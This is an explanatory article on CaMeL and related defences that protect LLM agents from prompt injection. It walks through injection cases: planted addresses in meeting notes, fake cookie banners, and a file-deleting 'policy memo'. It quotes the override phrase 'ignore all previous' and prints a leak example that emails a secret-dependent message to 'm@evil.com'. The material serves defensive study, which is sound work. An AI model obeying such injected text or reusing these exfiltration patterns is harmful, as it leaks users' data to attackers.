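# CaMeL: defending LLM agents against prompt injection by design

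## Prompt injection and the two-model design that CaMeL builds on

CaMeL (CApabilities for MachinE Learning) defends AI agents against prompt injection, an attack in which someone hides instructions in an email, web page or file that the agent will read. Edoardo Debenedetti and colleagues at Google DeepMind and ETH Zurich introduced it in March 2025 in *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design*. It limits what a fooled language model can do, but does not make the model harder to fool. It turns the user's request into a short program before reading any untrusted text. As the program runs, CaMeL tracks where each value came from and checks it before a tool acts on it. CaMeL extends a two-model design that the programmer Simon Willison proposed in 2023, and is easiest to understand as a fix for one specific flaw in that design.

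### Agents and the text they read

An agent is a large language model (LLM) that carries out a task by calling tools, which are functions that search a mailbox, send a message, open a file or pay a bill. The model only produces text, so ordinary code has to run the tools. *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants* (Willison, 2023) describes the usual arrangement. Developers tell the model to write something like `action:search_email(...)` whenever the task requires a search. The code scans the output for that pattern, runs the search and pastes the results into the model's next prompt. The cycle repeats until the model writes a final answer.

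Pasting a stranger's email into the same prompt as the user's request creates the vulnerability, because the model receives both as one stream of tokens, the word fragments it processes. Developers can label the parts, but models are only trained to follow the labels, and that training can fail on unusual input. In *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks* (2025), Willison compares this to SQL injection, an old class of attack in which a database runs part of a visitor's input as a command. Databases have a dependable fix for SQL injection, but Willison knew of none for prompt injection in language models.

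In an *indirect* prompt injection, the hostile text arrives in content that the agent fetches during a task. The user has no part in the attack and is usually unaware of it. *SecPO* (Chen, Peng and colleagues, 2026) cites a real incident in which an attacker opened an issue with a specially written title on the code-hosting site GitHub, and a coding agent read the title and ran the attacker's code.

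An attacker can target an agent's control flow or its data flow. Control flow is which tools the agent calls, in what order and under what conditions. Data flow is which values reach which tool arguments, and what those values derive from. *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* (Beurer-Kellner, Buesser et al., 2025) uses the example request "send today's schedule to my boss John Doe", which needs one call to read the calendar and one to send an email. A calendar entry that makes the agent forward the whole inbox to an outsider attacks control flow, because it adds a call. An entry that rewrites the body of the email to John Doe attacks data flow, because the agent makes the same calls but sends the attacker's text.

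### How AgentDojo scores agents and attackers

Much of the evidence on attacks and defences comes from one benchmark, *AgentDojo* (Debenedetti, Zhang and colleagues, 2024). It simulates four settings with 74 tools in total: an office workspace with email, calendar and cloud drive, a Slack messaging account, a travel agency and a bank. Each setting has user tasks, such as paying the bill in a named file, and attack goals, such as sending as much money as possible to the attacker's account. The benchmark pairs every user task with every attack goal in the same setting.

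| Suite | User tasks | Attack goals | Injected cases |
|---|---|---|---|
| Workspace | 40 | 14 | 560 |
| Slack | 21 | 5 | 105 |
| Travel | 20 | 7 | 140 |
| Banking | 16 | 9 | 144 |
| Total | 97 | 35 | 949 |

These are the counts for version 1.2.1, which Peng, Lian and colleagues (2026) used in *SecOPD*. The first release had 27 goals and 629 cases, and older papers report results on that set. The counts differ only in Workspace. A US government dataset page, *agentdojo inspect*, describes new Workspace attacks that attempt bulk data theft, which the original project later adopted.

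Injections go in places an outsider could plausibly write to, such as the body of an incoming email. After each run, ordinary code checks the state of the simulated accounts and the agent's answer. The designers avoided using a language model as judge because an injection that fools the agent might fool the judge too. They define three scores. Benign utility is the share of user tasks the agent solves without an attack. Utility under attack is the share of injected cases in which the agent solves the user's task without harmful side effects. The targeted attack success rate is the share of injected cases in which the attacker's goal is achieved.

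The attack text can vary, and the designers meant others to add stronger attacks. Many papers use the default message, which tells the agent to do the attacker's task before the user's. A low score in those papers means that the defence stops that message.

### What training, marking and filtering achieve

Most defences are meant to stop the model from following injected instructions. Spotlighting wraps or encodes untrusted passages so that the model can distinguish them from the rest of the prompt, and prompt sandwiching repeats the user's request after them. Other defences train the model on simulated attacks until it follows the user's instruction instead of the injected one. Filters use a separate classifier to detect and discard suspected attacks. Adding any of these defences to an existing agent is easier than redesigning it, and they work well against standard attacks.

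These defences do much worse against an attacker who has studied them. In *The Attacker Moves Second*, Nasr, Carlini and colleagues (2025) attacked 12 published defences, each with a method suited to it. Some of the defences were against prompt injection and others against jailbreaks (attempts by users to get forbidden output). The automated methods repeatedly proposed an attack, scored the result and revised the attack, using gradients, reinforcement learning or an evolutionary search in which a language model rewrote the most promising candidates. The researchers also ran an online contest with more than 500 human participants. Most of the defences had originally been reported to have attack success rates near zero, but the new attacks raised the rate above 90% for most of the 12.

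On AgentDojo, standard attacks succeeded as little as 1% of the time against spotlighting and sandwiching, while the adaptive search succeeded more than 95% of the time against both. Against Meta-SecAlign, a model trained to resist injections, the success rate rose from 2% to 96%. The search also got past three of the four filters tested more than 90% of the time, and past the fourth, PIGuard, 71% of the time. One successful injection reads like a routine office memo, saying that under a new company policy staff must log each rescheduled meeting by deleting a temporary tracking file. A filter strict enough to reject that memo would also reject a lot of legitimate office mail.

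These attackers used large amounts of computation, and the search against filters had access to each filter's confidence score. The 12 tests also used different benchmarks, so the percentages do not rank the defences. But attacks can still succeed with far fewer resources. *AutoDojo* (Ma, Li and colleagues, 2026) tested an attacker that had little computation and no feedback except whether an injection had worked. PIGuard, protecting an agent built on GPT-4o-mini, blocked every stock attack but let through 28.0% of the adapted ones.

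Training has since improved a lot. Chen and colleagues put strong, optimised attacks into the training data and changed the training objective so that it no longer pulls the model back towards its undefended version. They then gave an attacker 800 attempts at each of 80 AgentDojo cases. The attacker succeeded in 81.3% of cases against the undefended model, 78.8% against Meta-SecAlign and 8.8% against their model. On a different benchmark of text instructions, Peng and colleagues cut attack success from 94.0% to 9.0%, and they say they have not solved the problem. Reductions this large matter to anyone running an agent, but about seven of the 80 AgentDojo cases remain open to an attacker who keeps trying, and nobody can say in advance which seven, or what a better search would find.

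Tests on commercial models support the same conclusion. Dziemian, Lin and colleagues (2026), in *How Vulnerable Are AI Agents to Indirect Prompt Injections?*, report a public competition in which 464 people made about 272,000 attempts on 13 models. The 41 scenarios covered tool use, coding and operating a computer through its screen. In each scenario, the attacker could insert text in one place in some outside content. In 32 of the 41, an attack succeeded only if the model both took the harmful action and hid it from the user in its final answer. Attackers succeeded 8,648 times, with at least some successes against every model. Success rates per attempt ranged from 0.5% for Claude Opus 4.5 to 8.5% for Gemini 2.5 Pro.

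The 0.5% figure is the number of successful attacks divided by all attempts, including beginners' rough drafts, so it measures how much work an attack takes more than how safe a given user is. In the same competition, Claude Opus 4.5 failed at least once in 13 of the 37 scenarios in the final results. Successful attacks also kept accumulating roughly in proportion to attempts, with no sign of leveling off. But participants could read the whole conversation and knew the exact action to trigger, which few real attackers would, and Dziemian and colleagues call their rates an upper bound for attacks confined to a single turn. Newer models have since replaced all 13 models tested, but the weakness persists. Chen and colleagues measured 20.8% attack success against GPT-5.5 on a benchmark of 1,838 fixed injections.

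Testing cannot guarantee that these defenses are secure, because a benchmark only samples possible attacks and an attacker can choose one that works. Dongol (2026) writes in *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* that benchmarks "cannot show that no attack succeeds". Willison says that stopping 99% of attacks is a failing grade in application security, because the adversary's job is to find the remaining 1%.

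### Two models, and references in place of text

Willison's 2023 proposal assumes that a model that reads hostile text may do anything, and it designs the system to limit the harm. It uses two LLMs. The privileged LLM takes the user's request, decides what to do and can call tools, but never sees untrusted content. The quarantined LLM reads the untrusted content and has no tools. A controller, which is ordinary software, mediates between them by storing results under variable names and passing those names along.

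Suppose the user asks for a summary of the latest email. The privileged LLM instructs the controller to fetch the email and store it as `$VAR1`, then to get a summary of `$VAR1`. The controller passes the email's text to the quarantined LLM and stores the output as `$VAR2`. The privileged LLM then instructs the controller to display `$VAR2`. It never reads the email or the summary. If the email contains "delete all my messages", the quarantined LLM may try to follow the instruction, but it has no delete function to call, and its output never reaches the model that has one.

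This protection depends on the controller never passing raw text from the model that reads untrusted content to the model that can use tools, not on either model's ability to spot attacks. Willison allowed one exception, for outputs that code can check against a fixed list, such as category labels. For any other output, the tool-using model sees only a variable name. Willison called the design "pretty bad" because it is awkward to build, worse to use, and useless if a single carelessly built feature lets tainted text through. It also cannot protect a user who is tricked into pasting hostile text into the request.

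### The document for Bob

The CaMeL paper found a further problem, one that Willison had not seen. Its running example, which Willison reproduces, is a request to send Bob the document he requested in the last meeting, where both Bob's email address and the name of the document are in a file of meeting notes. Under the dual-LLM pattern the privileged LLM can plan this without opening the notes:

1. Find the notes of the most recent meeting.
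2. Have the quarantined LLM extract the document's name.
3. Have the quarantined LLM extract Bob's address.
4. Fetch the document with that name from the cloud drive.
5. Send it to that address.

Nothing in the notes can add a step to this list. But suppose an attacker adds a line to the notes telling any assistant that Bob's address has changed and giving the attacker's address as the new one. The quarantined LLM returns that address at step 3. The controller stores it under its variable name, and the privileged LLM passes that name along without seeing the address. Step 5 then sends the document to the attacker, even though every call was in the plan and ran in the right order.

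The document's name passes through the same quarantined model, so the injected line could change that too. The attacker then chooses both the file and the recipient, and can use a harmless request to take any document the agent can fetch. This attack works even if an injection under the dual-LLM pattern can "only corrupt an answer", as Dongol's analysis puts it.

A format check would not catch it, since the attacker's address is a valid address. Better training would not reliably catch it either, because the line in the notes need not be an instruction. It could be a false entry reading "Bob" followed by the wrong address, and a model that extracted it would be following its prompt correctly. Ma and colleagues class tasks like the user's as "param-open", meaning that the user names the action and leaves the details to be read from content, and they observe that people typically delegate details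 to agents in this way.

The dual-LLM pattern hides untrusted values from the planner but doesn't check whether they are safe to use. *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (2026) notes that values from the quarantined LLM later serve as tool arguments, so an attacker can do damage even while the agent keeps to its plan. For example, before the agent emails a private file to an address, the system needs to know where the address came from and who may read the file. The dual-LLM pattern doesn't record either fact. CaMeL attaches both to each value, in tags it calls capabilities, and checks them before the email is sent.

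## How CaMeL carries out a request: plans, capabilities and policies

The privileged LLM writes its program from the user's request and a description of each tool. An interpreter then runs the program, calling the quarantined LLM where the code requires it and making each tool call only if a policy allows it.

### The program is the plan

Willison explains the process with a small request: find Bob's address in my last email and send him a reminder about tomorrow's meeting. In simplified form, the privileged LLM writes something like this:

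```python
email = get_last_email()
address = query_quarantined_llm("Which address is Bob's?", email, output_schema=EmailStr)
send_email(recipient=address, subject="Tomorrow", body="Don't forget we meet tomorrow.")
```

The first line fetches the email. The second has the quarantined LLM extract an address from it, and the third sends the reminder. The privileged LLM could write the subject and body before the program ran because the request contained everything needed for them. The address wasn't in the request, so the program uses a variable for it.

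CaMeL's planner must finish the program before the first tool runs, so it has to write a branch in advance for anything that might happen. Fides, another defence built on two models, instead has its planner choose one action at a time without seeing the tool outputs. In *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too*, Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues (2026) measured the plans that CaMeL produces for AgentDojo tasks. The average plan had about 52 lines of code, five tool calls and four conditional branches.

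Because CaMeL's planner writes its code before any tool runs, it must also write code to parse results that nobody has seen yet. An ordinary agent can call a calendar tool, look at the output and work out which field holds the start time. CaMeL's planner needs the name of that field beforehand, and a wrong guess crashes the program. AgentDojo's standard tool descriptions leave this information out. In *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026) therefore did what CaMeL's designers had done for their own tests and added the full return format to every description. They consider this a modest job that a developer does once for each set of tools.

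The quarantined LLM must also return its answer in a fixed format. In the example, `EmailStr` means the answer must be an email address. Plans published by Peters-Gill and colleagues request a text answer and a yes/no field called `have_enough_info`, so the quarantined LLM can report that the material does not contain the answer. One of these plans lists the sensors on an industrial chiller that could reveal an overheating compressor. It queries one helper agent for the chiller's sensors and another for the relevant ones. If the query to the second helper returns an error, the plan retries it with different wording. The planner wrote this fallback before either helper had replied.

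Extracting an address is easier than planning a task and writing code for it, so CaMeL's designers suggest a smaller, cheaper model for the quarantined role, possibly one that runs on the user's own computer. If it ran there, the company that hosts the privileged LLM would see the request but none of the emails or files. The suggestion is plausible, but Peters-Gill and colleagues used the same model in both roles throughout their tests, so their results don't show how much a weaker quarantined model would reduce performance. A weaker model might also be easier to fool, and so return more wrong addresses.

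### How the interpreter tracks values

CaMeL runs the reminder program in a custom interpreter because an ordinary Python interpreter would not record where `address` came from. The custom interpreter uses Python's standard parser to turn the program into a syntax tree, a nested structure with a node for each assignment, call or condition, and evaluates the tree node by node. It links each value a node produces to the values used to compute it, so it records that `address` depends on `email`.

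The designers chose Python because language models already write it well, but the interpreter accepts only part of the language. A plan cannot define its own functions or use recursion, according to *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (2026), which presents a competing system called TACIT. Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues report in *CaMeLoT* (2026) that the interpreter also excludes arbitrary `while` loops. TACIT has agents write in full Scala 3 and uses the compiler to check the code before it runs, while CaMeL does its tracking during execution, which requires a special interpreter.

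Some dependencies do not show up in a tool's arguments. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow*, describe a program that emails an outsider only if an account balance is above some threshold. The text of the email is fixed, but the outsider can learn something about the balance from its arrival. For such cases, CaMeL's interpreter has a strict mode that adds a condition's tags to what happens inside the branch. The email then counts as derived from the balance, and the policy can block it.

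### What a capability records

A capability has two parts: the sources the value came from, and the readers who may see it. Garby and colleagues formalise it as a pair (*S*, *R*), where *S* is a set of sources and *R* is either a set of permitted readers or "unrestricted". When the program computes a new value from *a* and *b*, the new value gets all the sources of both and only the readers they have in common:

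$$S_{new} = S_a \cup S_b \qquad R_{new} = R_a \cap R_b$$

If a program summarizes two files, one that Alice and Bob may read and another that Bob and Carol may read, the summary's sources include both files. Only Bob may read the summary, because only he may read both files. Anything the program later derives from the summary keeps these sources and cannot gain readers.

In the reminder program the tags would look roughly like this:

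| Value | Sources | Readers |
|---|---|---|
| `email` | The mailbox, including whoever wrote the email | The user and the others on the email |
| `address` | The same email, by way of the quarantined LLM | The same people |
| Subject and body | The user's request, by way of the privileged LLM | Unrestricted |

The email's permitted readers follow the rule that Nikolaou and colleagues describe for a calendar event, where the user and the invitees determine who may read it. A plain trusted/untrusted label would be too coarse for such an event. Its description may be trustworthy if the user wrote it but not if someone else did, so two fields of one tool result can need different treatment. Such a label also doesn't show whether data is confidential. The user's own medical notes are a trustworthy source, but the agent still should not send them to a stranger.

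In computer security, "capability" has an older meaning: a token that grants authority to whoever holds it. For example, a program can open a file only if it holds a capability for that file. CaMeL's capabilities instead describe a value, and a separate policy determines what may be done with it. In Karp's mailing-list thread *Capabilities and prompt injection* (2025), Mark S. Miller, who coined the term "ocap" (object capability) for the older kind, wrote that CaMeL's tags "don't even sound vaguely like ocaps". They sounded to him like taint tracking, an established technique that marks suspect data and follows the marks through a program.

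In a quick reaction to a summary by Willison, Miller said he thought taint tracking could be very valuable against prompt injection, but he objected to the promise of hard guarantees. He argued that this kind of tracking suits code from a well-meaning but fallible author, and that stopping anything a malicious author might write would take a full information-flow system, which would also reject a lot of correct code.

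### Three possible recipients

A policy in CaMeL is a short Python function attached to a tool. It receives the requested call, the arguments and their capabilities, and returns "allowed" or "denied" with a reason. For the banking tool that changes a password, the policy checks whether the new password comes from a trusted source. If it doesn't, the policy denies the call and gives the reason that the password does not come from the user. Because policies are ordinary code, instructions in an email cannot override them, but someone has to write them for every tool.

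For the reminder, Willison proposes that reading the last email is always allowed, but sending an email is allowed only if the recipient is trusted. The policy can't decide this from the source tag alone, because `address` always comes from the email and would always fail, so it also has to check the address itself. If the user's settings already mark the address as trusted, CaMeL sends the reminder without interrupting the user, but if the address is unfamiliar, it can ask the user to approve the message.

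Now suppose an attacker planted the address in the email. The policy cannot detect this, but the address does not match a trusted contact, so the user has to decide. If the user approves without checking, the reminder goes to the attacker. An attacker could also plant the address of someone the user trusts. This rule would then let the message go to the wrong colleague, which hardly matters for a reminder but could matter for a confidential file.

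The readers half of the capability protects the confidential file, because a policy can require every recipient of an email to be a permitted reader of its contents. In the example of the document for Bob, the attacker is not a permitted reader, so the policy denies the call. Garby and colleagues apply a similar rule to payments in their own system. The recipient of a transfer must be trusted and allowed to read the amount, subject and date.

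A policy protects only the arguments it checks. Garby and colleagues rebuilt the reminder example in their own small programming language, adding an injected postscript in which "Bob" mentions a family emergency and asks for a cancellation note instead. An agent that kept everything in one conversation, running on GPT-4o, sent the cancellation, while one that wrote its program first, running on GPT-5.2, sent the reminder. The models differ, but the second result did not depend on GPT-5.2 detecting the injection, because the subject and body were already fixed in the program when the model read the email. Their policy requires the subject and body to be trusted but does not check the recipient, so it would allow a planted address. Willison's rule is meant to catch a planted address but would allow a tampered body if the recipient were a known contact, so a careful deployment would use both.

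### When a program fails

The privileged LLM writes the program without seeing the data, so the program can crash, for instance if a field is missing or a date is in an unexpected format. CaMeL then gives the privileged LLM the type and location of the error and prompts it for corrected code, for up to ten attempts.

Error messages can carry an attack. When Python fails to convert text into a number, its standard error message repeats the text. If that text came from an email, forwarding the message could show an attacker's words to the privileged LLM, which must never read untrusted data. CaMeL therefore removes the message whenever it depends on untrusted data, and the privileged LLM has to repair the program using the remaining error information.

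This repair loop runs outside the interpreter that does the tracking. Garby and colleagues point out that each new attempt starts with clean tags, even though the planner wrote it in response to the previous one's outcome. Censoring the messages reduces the problem but gives no formal guarantee, and repeated failures can leak information. Garby and colleagues also warn that an agent that gets stuck partway through a live run can accidentally repeat actions, such as a payment that had already gone through.

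The agent built by Garby and colleagues first tests its program on invented data, where payments do nothing and every file contains the same placeholder text. It revises the program until it runs without errors, then writes the version that will run on the real account. The agent can't recover if that version fails, which Garby and colleagues list as a considerable weakness. Peters-Gill and colleagues took the simpler approach of leaving retries out of their version of CaMeL.

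### Checking the whole plan in advance

A CaMeL policy checks a single call just before the program makes it. Nikolaou and colleagues illustrate the limitation of this with an agent in a security operations centre, where analysts investigate alerts about possible break-ins. One rule there is that nobody may isolate a computer from the network without approval from the incident response team. The policy on the isolation tool receives the call and its arguments, which don't include an earlier request for approval. A developer could work around this by making the approval an argument of the isolation tool, so that the approval's tag would show where it came from.

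There is no such workaround for another of their rules, which requires the agent to eventually resolve or escalate every incident ticket it opens. An agent breaks this rule by never making a call, and a policy that runs only when there is a call can't detect that. Another drawback is that CaMeL detects a violation at a plan's last step only after running all the earlier steps.

CaMeLoT, released in September 2026, adds a check between writing the plan and running it. It converts the program into a finite-state machine, with states for the points in the program and transitions for the possible next steps. It labels the states with the tools called so far and with whether each argument could come from an untrusted source. Developers write their rules in computation tree logic, a formal language for statements about all the ways a process might unfold. For isolating a computer, the approval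 rule comes down to this:

```
AG (call_isolate_host → request_ir_approval_called)
```

`AG` means "in every state on every path". A program called a model checker searches the possible paths for one that breaks the rule. If it finds one, CaMeLoT describes the path to the privileged LLM, requests a repaired plan and checks again, until a plan passes or CaMeLoT reaches the repair limit. This feedback needs no censoring, because no tool has run yet and no untrusted text has entered the system.

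The formula is weaker than the rule in words because it only requires the plan to ask for approval at some point before isolating the computer, whatever the answer. Nikolaou and colleagues' example of a safe plan asks for approval, does not store the reply, and then isolates the computer. CaMeLoT also ignores the conditions in `if` statements and treats every branch as possible, so it could not check whether a plan acts on a refusal. That check would have to happen at run time.

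In their first experiment, Nikolaou and colleagues tried to reproduce CaMeL's own policies for AgentDojo as advance checks, and managed it for 22 of 28. The others depend on facts that exist only at run time, such as who can currently open a shared file. They then ran both systems on the 97 user tasks, without attacks, using Claude Haiku 4.5:

| Outcome | Tasks |
|---|---|
| Both allowed the plan, and it worked | 42 |
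| Both blocked the plan | 17 |
| Only CaMeLoT let a working plan through | 9 |
| Only CaMeL let a working plan through | 7 |
| The plan failed to do the task under both | 22 |

The systems agreed on 59 of the 75 tasks that remain after excluding the 22 failures. CaMeLoT runs in addition to CaMeL, so a plan has to satisfy both. On these figures, CaMeL alone completes 49 tasks and the combination completes 42. The combination completes seven fewer because CaMeLoT treats any value as suspect if it cannot establish the value's origin in advance. The experiment switched off plan repair for policy violations, and repair might recover some of those seven tasks.

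The second experiment used the security operations centre. Nikolaou and colleagues wrote one safe plan and seven unsafe variants, each breaking a different rule. CaMeLoT caught all seven, while a simplified CaMeL caught only the one that passed an untrusted network address to a blocking tool. The researchers had designed the rules to go beyond what CaMeL can express, so the result confirms that the mechanism works but is little evidence of how often such rules matter in practice. In a follow-up, the language model wrote the plans itself from requests meant to produce bad ones, and CaMeLoT caught all four. One request came from a hurried user who told the agent to skip the approval, so the rules protected the organisation from its own staff even though nobody had injected anything.

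A plan can obey every security rule and still not do what the user wanted. The third experiment therefore had a language model derive requirements from the request itself, for example that changing the password must remain possible after the agent has checked the transactions. The model picks from a fixed list of requirement types and trusted code writes the formulas, because models that wrote formulas directly sometimes referred to tools or facts that did not exist. Writing directly, GPT-4.1 nano produced fully valid formulas for only 12 of the 97 AgentDojo tasks, although Claude Haiku 4.5 did so for 96. With the fixed list, every formula was valid. In 20 prepared cases, the derived rules accepted every correct plan and blocked every faulty one. But a valid formula can still state the wrong requirement. The model correctly identified the requested actions in 88 of the 97 tasks, even when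 given credit for actions that depend on a condition. In the other nine, CaMeLoT would enforce a requirement that the user had not asked for or miss one that they had.

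## What CaMeL guarantees and where the guarantee stops

CaMeL's protection assumes that the user's request is honest, the tool descriptions are trustworthy and the policies are correct. If any of these assumptions is false, CaMeL can run as designed and still do what an attacker wants.

Tallam and Miller (2025), in *Operationalizing CaMeL*, point out that phishing can lead a user to pass a crafted prompt to the agent as a request. They propose screening requests for suspicious links and phrases like "ignore all previous", but this brings back the kind of filter that adaptive attackers beat. Tool descriptions are also a risk because many agents load them from outside servers through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a standard way of connecting agents to tools. Zingrillo, Foerster and colleagues (2026), in *Securing Computer-Use Agents Against Branch Steering Attacks*, describe servers that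 hide instructions in a description or change it after the user has approved it. CaMeL's privileged LLM reads these descriptions, so the attack bypasses the quarantine. People also write the policies by hand and may leave gaps in them.

### Three properties of rising strength

Control-flow integrity is the weakest of the relevant properties. Peters-Gill and colleagues define it for agents as keeping execution within a plan that depends only on the user's request and other trusted information. Untrusted data may affect which branch of the plan runs, but it cannot add a branch or a tool call.

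Policy-enforced data flow adds a check on values. Peters-Gill and colleagues call an agent "CaMeL-secure" under a set of policies if it has control-flow integrity and every tool call must satisfy those policies. If the set is empty, the definition reduces to control-flow integrity, so any added protection depends on the policies someone has written.

Noninterference is stronger than either. It means that changing the protected inputs does not change what an observer sees. If the protected input is a bank balance, an outsider sees the same emails whatever the balance is. If it is an attacker's text, the agent's trusted outputs are the same whatever the attacker writes.

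CaMeL aims for the first two properties and does not offer noninterference. It also has no soundness theorem, a proof that its interpreter catches every data flow it is supposed to catch. Garby and colleagues note that CaMeL's designers call formalisation a "crucial direction" for further work. Fides has a noninterference theorem, but for one fixed agent loop. CaMeL's planner writes a new program for each request, so a theorem for CaMeL would have to cover any program the planner might write.

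### Choosing among branches the plan already has

Suppose a user asks an agent to read an email and, if it is a meeting request, add the meeting to the calendar. The plan must contain a branch that changes the calendar, and the sender's text determines whether that branch runs. Foerster and colleagues use the term "branch steering" for attacks in which false data makes a plan take a branch it already contains. The attacker adds no action to the plan, so control-flow integrity still holds.

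CaMeL's strict mode can mark the calendar entry as dependent on the email, and a policy can then block it. But a legitimate invitation carries the same mark, so CaMeL asks the user to tell the two apart. *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* (2026) objects that the attacker can then try to deceive the user, and that approval requests wear the user out. It says the deepest open problem in the area is the lack of a principled account of which such tasks can be made secure.

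Branch steering is much easier against agents that operate a computer through its screen. A planner that can't see the screen has to prepare for pop-ups, login pages and failed clicks, and the plans Foerster and colleagues generated had about 40 branches on average, compared with four for AgentDojo. Policies also help much less here, because they can check the recipient of a `send_email` call but only the coordinates of a `click(x, y)` call. The same click could open a tab or confirm a bank transfer.

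Foerster and colleagues put a fake cookie notice inside an advertising banner. Almost any plan for using the web includes closing cookie notices, so an attacker can count on that branch without knowing the user's task. The agent looked for a cookie notice, found the fake one and clicked through to the attacker's site. Comparing the screenshot with the page's code stopped this on static banners, where the code marked the frame as an advertisement, but failed on banners whose code the attacker could write. Using other models to check the result didn't filter out the fake notices without also rejecting many real ones. In another attack, small changes to a banner's pixels made the vision model return false but plausible coordinates, which also got past the checks. Stealing money this way would be harder, since it would take several coordinated deceptions that fit a specific plan.

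Zingrillo and colleagues then built a benchmark of 101 tasks for this type of attack. Attacks succeeded in 94.4% of cases against an ordinary agent and in 89.5% against one with a separate planner but no data-flow policies, so control-flow integrity alone gave very little protection. In their defence, COBRA, the planner limits which sites every branch may contact, which operations it may perform and which values it may send before the agent reads anything untrusted. COBRA then checks the web request that a click produces, because a request to approve a loan, unlike the click, has a definite address and named fields.

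COBRA blocked all 199 attack cases in a benchmark that counts an attack as successful when it breaks the limits in force. COBRA enforces those same limits, so an outside benchmark of web attacks is more informative. There, when COBRA had only a list of allowed sites, all 14 attacks that misused an allowed site succeeded. It blocked all 14 once it also had a list of each site's operations. It still can't check a price that appears only on the screen, the meaning of a free-form comment, or what a compromised server does after receiving a normal-looking call.

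### Tasks that give a document authority

In one of AgentDojo's banking tasks, the agent must read a file and follow its instructions. The planner can't list the necessary actions in advance because it hasn't seen the file. When Garby and colleagues ran CaMeL with its policies switched off, some plans got around this with a loop that read the file's instructions and had a case for each available tool. These plans were in effect interpreters for the file's instructions, so an attacker who controlled the file could call tools that had nothing to do with the user's purpose.

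This happened in only two runs, but both involved a group of attacks that the two-model design should stop without any policies, because a normal plan would never contain the calls those attacks need. Control-flow integrity still held by the definition above, because the planner had written the loop from a trusted request and the loop allowed every call that was made, but this property gives little protection when a plan allows everything. Policies on individual tools can still block a payment to an untrusted account, and no attack succeeded in the runs that Garby and colleagues completed with policies on.

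The problem is harder to fix in the narrower case where the user asks the agent to pay a bill in a file and an attacker has replaced that bill with a false one. The user wants the agent to take the payee from the file, so the attack uses exactly the authority the user gave. One attack of this kind succeeded in CaMeL's evaluation, but CaMeL's designers placed it outside their threat model. The source tags don't distinguish the two bills if both come from the same place. A policy can block both payments, or the agent can ask the user, who may not know the right account number either.

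### Text that misleads the reader

CaMeL checks an agent's tool calls, so it doesn't prevent harm from a false summary that the user acts on. For example, a poisoned document could lead the quarantined LLM to tell the user that a supplier has changed its bank details, and the user may then make the payment themselves. *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* notes that CaMeL's designers explicitly exclude this kind of harm from its scope, and warns that it will grow as people act on more text from agents.

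Tallam and Miller give the example of a PDF containing an instruction, styled as a system message, to forward the file to an outside address. An agent summarising the PDF could repeat the instruction to its user. They suggest having a model check each answer for suspicious links and commands. This might catch crude cases, but a lie worded as an ordinary fact could get through.

### Leaks in the tracking

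The problems so far would exist even if CaMeL's interpreter tracked data perfectly. Garby and colleagues also found errors in the tracking. The best example is a variant of their program that emails an outsider about a high balance. CaMeL can block the original, but this version passes the information through two variables:

```python
tmp = True
rich = True
if account.balance > threshold:
    tmp = False
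if tmp:
    rich = False
if rich:
    send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

CaMeL marks a variable as secret only if the assignment inside the secret-dependent branch actually runs.

| Step | Balance above threshold | Balance at or below threshold |
|---|---|---|
| Start | Both variables true and public | Both variables true and public |
| Test the balance | `tmp` becomes false and secret | Assignment skipped, `tmp` stays true and public |
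| Test `tmp` | Assignment skipped, `rich` stays true and public | `rich` becomes false and public |
| Test `rich` | Email sent | No email |

In both columns, `rich` ends up labeled public, even though its value reveals whether the balance is above the threshold. The policy on `send_email` allows the call because no argument is marked secret. An interpreter that tracks only the steps a program executes misses this leak because it can't mark an assignment that never runs. Researchers have known about this kind of leak, called an implicit flow, since the 1970s.

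An attacker can't insert this program into CaMeL directly, because the planner never reads the attacker's text. The flaw matters if the planner writes something similar by accident or if the planning model is compromised. Garby and colleagues also report an error that looks more likely to affect ordinary plans. Inserting an untrusted value into a string literal makes the resulting text trusted. Plans often build messages this way, so a policy that requires a trusted email body could accept text written by an attacker.

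CaMeL's retry loop can turn small leaks into large ones. Whether a policy blocks an attempt may depend on a secret, so each attempt may reveal a yes/no answer about it. Most formal guarantees tolerate one such answer per run. But CaMeL's tracking doesn't cover the loop, so a later attempt can build on that answer to reveal another, and 20 answers are enough to identify a balance between zero and a million dollars to the nearest dollar. CaMeL limits each request to ten attempts, but a series of requests can leak more.

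Other leaks come from how a program behaves while it runs. Tallam and Miller describe a loop that fetches a web page once for each unit of a secret number, so anyone with the site's access log can count the visits. An error that occurs only when a secret meets some condition reveals one bit, and a delay whose length depends on a secret reveals more. CaMeL's designers demonstrated two leaks against their own system, one through an indirect dependency and one through an error, and discussed a third through timing, so Tallam and Miller are wrong to say that CaMeL "omits side-channel concerns". According to *PolicySniff* (2026), strict mode deals with the two demonstrated cases, and the interpreter doesn't provide the clock function that the timing example needs.

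Even with the clock removed so that a plan can't measure time, an outsider can still time the requests that arrive. *PolicySniff* studies an observer whose program shares a graphics processor with the language model. The observer times that program's work to infer which policy state the model is running under. This involves no tool call, so CaMeL has nothing to check.

### A version with machine-checked proofs

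Garby and colleagues responded with LLMbda, a small programming language for agents, with its own proofs. Every value carries a label, and every step of execution passes labels on. If a branch that depends on a secret tries to change the public conversation with a model, LLMbda stops the program. Someone may still learn one bit from the stop, but the agent's retries happen inside the tracked language, so they can't repeat the leak with clean labels.

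The main theorem is a form of noninterference that allows for two complications: language models give random answers, and programs may fail to finish. Take two inputs that differ only in ways an observer isn't allowed to see. Let $\mu(q)$ and $\nu(q)$ be the probabilities that the observer sees outcome $q$ in each case, and let $d_\mu$ and $d_\nu$ be the probabilities that the program doesn't finish. Then

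$$\frac{1}{2}\sum_q |\mu(q)-\nu(q)| \;\le\; \frac{d_\mu+d_\nu}{2}$$

If the program always finishes, the two distributions are identical. If it fails to finish 2% of the time in both cases, they differ by at most two percentage points. The proof compares both runs with a hypothetical third run, which replaces a computation with a dummy value as soon as it depends on something hidden from the observer. This third run is the same for both inputs and produces each visible outcome at least as often as either real run, which limits how much the two distributions can differ.

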